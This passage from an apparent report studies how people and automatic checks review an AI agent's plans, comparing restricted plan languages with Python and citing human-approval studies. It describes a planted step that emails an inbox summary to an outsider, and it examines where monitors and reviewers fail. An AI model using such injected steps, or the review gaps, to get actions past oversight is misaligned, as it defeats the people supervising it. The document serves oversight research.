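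A restricted language also makes the evaluation more reliable. The ask plan has only two possible sequences of calls, one that ends with the question and one that goes on to delete the table. An evaluator who estimates how bad and how likely each sequence would be has covered everything the plan can do. An evaluator can also judge a plan written in ordinary Python or English, but it is harder to be sure the estimate covers every possible run.

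The firm would also need to ask for more than one plan. Neither SPA nor Soteria compares alternatives. If the planner were equally likely to write any of the three database plans, the firm's average loss at *p* = 5% would be $456, compared with $150 if it saw all three and chose the best.

Comparing more plans, like allowing more retries, creates more chances for error. If an evaluator badly underestimates the harm of 1% of harmful plans, the chance that it does so at least once in ten independent harmful plans is again 9.6%. The firm may then choose the misjudged plan because the mistake makes it look good. Running the checks first reduces this risk, because a plan that breaks a stated rule never reaches the evaluator.

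## Whether restricted plans are easier for people to review

Someone will still have to read some of the firm's plans, however good its checks are, and a restricted language may help most with that reading. Even if the language guaranteed nothing about safety, its plans would usually be short and use only a few constructs. A reader could see a plan's effects from its text, and a planner would have few places to hide an effect.

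### One task in two languages

Suppose the owner asks the assistant to send a reminder to every client who is more than 30 days late in paying. In the firm's language, the plan might be:

```
1  note = read_file("reminder.txt")
2  unpaid = query_db("invoices", "unpaid")
3  for inv in unpaid:
4      if inv.days_late > 30:
5          send_mail(inv.email, "Reminder", note)
```

An ordinary Python program for the same task might be:

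```python
1  from firm_tools import read_file, query_db, send_mail
2  from late import select
3
4  note = read_file("reminder.txt")
5  unpaid = query_db("invoices", "unpaid")
6  for inv in select(unpaid, days=30):
7      send_mail(inv.email, "Reminder", note.format(inv=inv))
```

The two look much alike, and the Python version can put each client's name in the message, which the plan can't. But two features of the Python version give the reviewer extra work. It imports the function `select` from another file, `late`, and the import runs all the code in that file. The `format` operation fills in blanks in the reminder, and the text of the reminder determines what goes into them. If someone has added `{inv.staff_comment}` to `reminder.txt`, each client will receive whatever the staff wrote about them.

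| What the reviewer must work out | Restricted plan | Python program |
|---|---|---|
| Which tools can run? | The three in the text | Those three, and anything the code in `late` uses |
| How many emails can it send? | At most one per unpaid invoice | It depends on what `select` returns |
| What will each email contain? | The text of `reminder.txt` | That text, plus any invoice fields named in it |
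| Who will receive the emails? | The addresses in the database | The same, unless `select` changes them |
| Are the addresses and the text correct? | Look them up | Look them up |

A careful programmer could write the Python as plainly as the plan, but the reviewer would still have to read the whole program to confirm this and know Python well enough to recognize the risky features. The firm's grammar excludes those features from every plan, so the reviewer never has to look for them.

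*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026), a study of 290 reports of agents damaging files, gives a more extreme example. An approval prompt for the command `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it authorizes whatever code is in the script.

### Turning a plan into prose

Many users can't read even a simple program, so Meijer converts each plan into a few sentences of English that follow it step by step. For example, his plan with the planted step that emails the inbox summary to an outsider is stored as JSON, a data format full of brackets and quotation marks. A user could easily miss that step in the JSON, but it has its own sentence in the English version.

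That sentence also begins "For compliance purposes", which is the attacker's excuse. The firm could keep the excuse out by generating the prose only from tool names, arguments and conditions. Its grammar has four kinds of step, so a short program with a sentence pattern for each step and tool could translate any plan. The plan above would become: "Read the file reminder.txt. Look up the unpaid invoices. For each one that is more than 30 days late, send the text of the file to the address on the invoice, with the subject Reminder."

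An AI model would describe the plan in smoother prose, but the description might be wrong. In early user research for *When Should Users Check?* (2025), the most frequent agent error was a mismatch between what the agent described and what it did. Anthropic removes the agent's explanations before auto mode judges an action, so that the agent cannot persuade the judge to make a bad decision. Hiding these explanations from human reviewers could protect them in the same way.

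### Experiments on reading small languages

A plan language is a domain-specific language, one made for a single kind of task. Kosar, Mernik and Carver (2012), in *Program comprehension of domain-specific and general-purpose languages*, compared such languages with general-purpose languages in three experiments, each in a different domain. Developers understood programs written in the domain-specific languages more accurately and efficiently.

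Kosar and others repeated the experiments in 2018, letting the developers use normal programming software and giving each of them only one kind of language. The results were consistent with the first ones. In a review of the replication, *Program Comprehension of Domain-Specific and General-Purpose Languages*, Wilson (2021) concludes that the burden of proof is now on people who doubt the benefit. The participants were new to the small languages, so the experiments may have understated the benefit. Wilson notes that many small languages are badly designed, and would still like to see them compared with well-designed ones.

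In *Can a domain-specific language improve program structure comprehension of data pipelines?* (2025), Heltweg, Schwarz and Riehle tested how well 57 students understood the structure of programs that download, clean and store data. Each student read one program in Python and another in Jayvee, a small language designed for this work, and picked each program's steps from a list and put them in order.

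| | Jayvee | Python |
|---|---|---|
| Students with every step right | 41 of 57 | 22 of 57 |
| Missed that the program selects only some columns | 2 | 13 |
| Missed that the program downloads a file | 0 | 4 |
| Median time | 252 seconds | 234 seconds |

A mistake like the missed download matters for safety. The Python programs used `read_csv`, which can open a file on the computer or download one from the internet, and the code for the two differs only in the file's address. Jayvee has a separate construct for each. The students rated the two languages about equally easy to understand, although most had misread the Python, so a reviewer may not notice when a program has become too hard to read.

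Showing reviewers how steps connect can also help. In *From Review to Reuse* (2026), people who reviewed an agent's finished work as a structured workflow recalled 94% of its major steps on average, significantly more than people who reviewed it as a chat. In one task, the agent read a list of existing reviews but never used it to filter out old ones before updating a spreadsheet. The workflow showed this missing connection, which was hard to detect from the result. In the firm's language, the same mistake would leave a variable that no later line uses, which a checker could flag.

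All these experiments tested comprehension, and none tested whether people notice that a program would do harm. A reviewer can understand `delete_table("customers")` without knowing whether to approve it. The small languages also had a vocabulary suited to their tasks, so we can't tell how much of the benefit came from leaving constructs out. Even with Jayvee, 16 of the 57 students made a mistake.

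### Plausible plans

*Plan-Then-Execute* (He, Demartini and Gadiraju, 2025) studied how well people judge an AI agent's plans. The study gave 248 people six everyday tasks, each with a plan written in English by GPT-3.5, an early model. Three of the plans had flaws. Some participants could edit the plans, some could step in while the agent carried them out, some could do both, and some could do neither. The table shows how many participants in the two groups that could not edit plans trusted each one, and how often the agent got the right result when nobody intervened.

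| Task | Flaw in the plan | Trusted the plan | Right result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Exchange currency | Puts two transactions in one step | 80–89% | 0% |
| Pay a credit card | Never looks up the full card number | 79–89% | 78% |
| Book a TV repair | Last step matches no available tool | 90–97% | 44% |
| Set alarms | None | 94–97% | 95% |
| Book flights | None | 84–87% | 98% |
| Plan a trip | None | 81% | 6% |

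People trusted the flawed plans about as often as the sound ones. This was sometimes reasonable, since the agent usually paid the credit card correctly despite the flaw. But at least 80% of these participants trusted the currency plan, which failed every time because the agent carried out only one transaction per step. One participant said of the planning stage that they "mostly left the default plans (they looked fine)".

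Letting people edit the plans raised average quality slightly on the currency task, from 2.0 to about 2.4 out of 5. But it lowered the scores of all three plans that were already sound, from 5.0 to between 4.3 and 4.8.

A restricted language would have made these flaws easier to catch. The firm's grammar allows only one tool call per step, so a planner could not combine two transactions. A checker would reject a step that names no available tool, and a tool contract could require a full card number. The reviewer would then see only plans without these flaws, but those plans might look even more trustworthy.

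The flaws were honest mistakes, as they were in related work. *An Experimental Comparison of Cognitive Forcing Functions for Execution Plans* (2026), for example, planted missing, unnecessary, incorrect and misordered steps in plans for writing tasks. Studies of how people approve single actions come closer to testing whether people notice harm.

### How often people catch harmful actions

Anthropic hired 1,053 testers for a coding study and, partway through each session, replaced one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. The testers had less reason to be careful because they were not working on their own projects, and Anthropic was arguing for its automatic check, but it is hard to attribute such a low rate to these factors alone.

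People review an agent's actions better when they have more information. Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, asked 80 volunteers to approve or refuse 12 actions each, half of them harmful. In one example, a user wants an auditor to receive only summary totals. The agent copies the full invoice records into a report, then asks to send the report to the auditor. The tool and the recipient are both allowed, so only someone who knows what went into the report can see the harm. The volunteers saw one of four prompts.

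| What the prompt showed | Harmful actions approved | Harmless actions approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| The exact tool call | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| The call, the user's instructions and a log of earlier steps | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, with their combined effect stated | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

The last improvement could be due to chance, because each group had only 20 people. The overall trend favors written plans, which contain the exact calls and show where each argument comes from. But even with the best prompt, the volunteers approved about a quarter of the harmful actions. When the harm depended on a chain of steps, they approved 7 of 30 harmful actions with each of the last two prompts, so stating the combined effect made no difference.

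Neither study used restricted plans, so neither directly tested whether such plans are easier to review. An experiment could test this by having people look for harmful steps in restricted plans and in equivalent Python.

### Approval fatigue

People who must approve many actions soon stop reading them. Anthropic reports that users of its coding agent approve 97% of permission prompts. Many turn the prompts off, and 80 of the 290 reports of file damage in *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* involved automatic approval.

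A plan can replace many permission prompts with one. If 40 clients are late in paying, the reminder plan makes 42 tool calls, and an agent that needed permission for each would interrupt the owner 42 times. People also seem to take plans more seriously than prompts for single calls, since Anthropic's users reject 39% of the plans they see. This doesn't show that they catch harmful plans, because a user may reject a plan just to get a different approach.

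Letting users set rules in advance may reduce the burden less than hoped. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (2026), Yan had 113 people without a software background supervise an agent through 18 actions, seven of which went beyond what the user had requested. One group first chose "allow", "ask" or "never" for four kinds of action, such as spending money. They chose "ask" for 114 of 140 rules, so they still had to make most decisions later. About 60% of the unrequested actions went ahead in this group, compared with about 40% in the group that approved every action individually. Users had personally approved 133 of the 148 unrequested actions that went ahead under the rules.

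Odersky and colleagues respond to reviewer fatigue with TACIT, which they designed so that the compiler can establish that an agent's program leaks no secrets and people can rely on this "without reviewing the agent's code". The compiler can do this for properties that the types express, but someone still has to decide whether the user wants the program's other effects.

### Arguments and long plans

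A simple structure doesn't help reviewers when the harm is in an argument. `delete_table("orders_2015")` and `delete_table("orders_2025")` differ by one digit, and few people would notice a wrong account number in a payment. The firm can reduce this problem by showing what each argument refers to. The prompt could show, next to the table's name, that the table has 48,000 rows and that someone changed it this morning. A program can find every argument in a restricted plan and look up the fixed ones, which is much harder in Python.

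A restriction can also make plans longer. The firm's grammar has no way to write out a list, so a plan that sends a price list to twelve named clients needs twelve separate `send_mail` lines. If one of the twelve addresses belongs to a competitor, a tired reviewer may skip over it. The best remedy is to add the missing construct:

```
1  prices = read_file("prices.txt")
2  for a in ["ann@alder.example", "bo@birch.example", ...]:
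3      send_mail(a, "Prices", prices)
```

The loop still runs over a finite list, so every plan stops. The reviewer can now see that each client gets the same message, but still has to check twelve addresses. Sub-plans, which Soteria uses, similarly avoid repeating a group of steps. A firm that wants readable plans should choose its restrictions partly by looking at the plans its planner writes. Extra length does not always slow readers down. Jayvee is wordier than Python, but the students took about the same time to read each.

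### How much attention the checks save

Suppose the firm's assistant writes 200 plans a day and a reviewer spends three minutes on each. The reviews take ten hours, more than a working day. If automatic checks clear 90% of the plans, the reviewer has 20 left and needs one hour. Gregor Stewart, a security executive quoted in *Agentic AI systems are doing more and more work* (Oreskovic, 2026), says that otherwise people have so much to audit "that you can't truly be accountable".

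Without the checks, a reviewer with only one hour would have 18 seconds per plan. In the study by Hossain and colleagues, volunteers given the barest prompt spent about as long, 16.3 seconds, and approved 55% of harmful actions.

Whether the saving is safe depends on which plans the checks clear. Suppose 2% of the plans, or four a day, are harmful. As a rough guide, suppose too that the reviewer misses a quarter of the harmful plans after three minutes' reading and 55% after 18 seconds. If the checks clear *m* of the four, the number that run each day is:

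```
m + (4 − m)/4  =  1 + 0.75m
```

| Method | Reviewer's time | Harmful plans that run per day |
|---|---|---|
| Read all 200 carefully | 10 hours | 1.0 |
| Read all 200 for 18 seconds each | 1 hour | 2.2 |
| Checks clear 180 plans, none harmful | 1 hour | 1.0 |
| Checks clear 180 plans, one harmful | 1 hour | 1.75 |
| Checks clear 180 plans at random | 1 hour | 3.7 |
| Checks clear all 200 because they all stop | none | 4.0 |

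If the firm has one hour for review, the checks work better than skimming as long as the checks let through fewer than 1.6 of the four harmful plans. The reviewer would probably miss more harmful plans than estimated here, because half the actions in the experiment were harmful and people tend to be less alert when harm is rare.

The checks cannot establish that a plan is what the owner meant, so they should clear a plan only if the worst it could do would be acceptable even if the planner had misunderstood the request. For example, the firm might clear any plan that deletes nothing, pays nobody, and sends mail only to the owner. It could also clear small payments to accounts in its supplier table, with a daily limit on their total across all plans.

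The 90% figure is an assumption, and strict checks may clear far fewer plans. SPA's label check rejected about 53% of its runs on AgentDojo. If the same share of the firm's plans went to the reviewer, reading them would take more than five hours.

Reading a sample of the cleared plans is a weak test of the checks. If the reviewer reads 100 of them and finds nothing harmful, this shows, with 95% confidence, only that fewer than about 3% are harmful, and the rate was 2% before any checks. A better test is to submit known harmful plans, without running them, and count how many the checks clear. Mixing a few into the plans the reviewer reads would test the reviewer too, and might help keep them alert.

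### A procedure for the reviewer

Suppose the owner asks the assistant to remove old clients from the database, and the checks send this plan to a reviewer:

```
1  old = query_db("clients", "inactive")
2  for c in old:
3      delete_records(c)
```

1. **Leave to the checker what it can settle.** This includes which tools the plan can call, whether fixed arguments are within the limits, where data can go, the largest possible total, and the order of steps. The reviewer should confirm which of these checks the plan passed, and that neither the plan nor the rules have changed since, but need not repeat them by eye.

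2. **Compare the request with the tool calls.** The reviewer should read the user's own words first and ignore any explanation from the planner. Here the owner said "old" and the planner chose "inactive", which may mean something else.

3. **Look up what the text does not show.** The reviewer should find out what each name and filter refers to now, how many items the plan would affect, and whether anyone could undo the result. Suppose the filter matches 212 clients, three of them have open orders, and the firm has no recent backup.

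4. **Ask the user about the effect.** "May I run `delete_records`?" invites a quick yes. A better question is "This will permanently delete the records of 212 clients, including three with open orders. Is that what you want?" The reviewer should ask only when the answer could change the decision, since needless questions cause fatigue.

5. **Refuse if an important question remains open.** If the plan could do serious or permanent harm, the reviewer should refuse it when the user is unsure, when nobody can find out what an argument refers to, or when the plan is too long to read with care. The reviewer should then request a new plan instead of editing the old one, and send it through every check again. If the new plan only splits a forbidden action into smaller ones, the reviewer should refuse that too.
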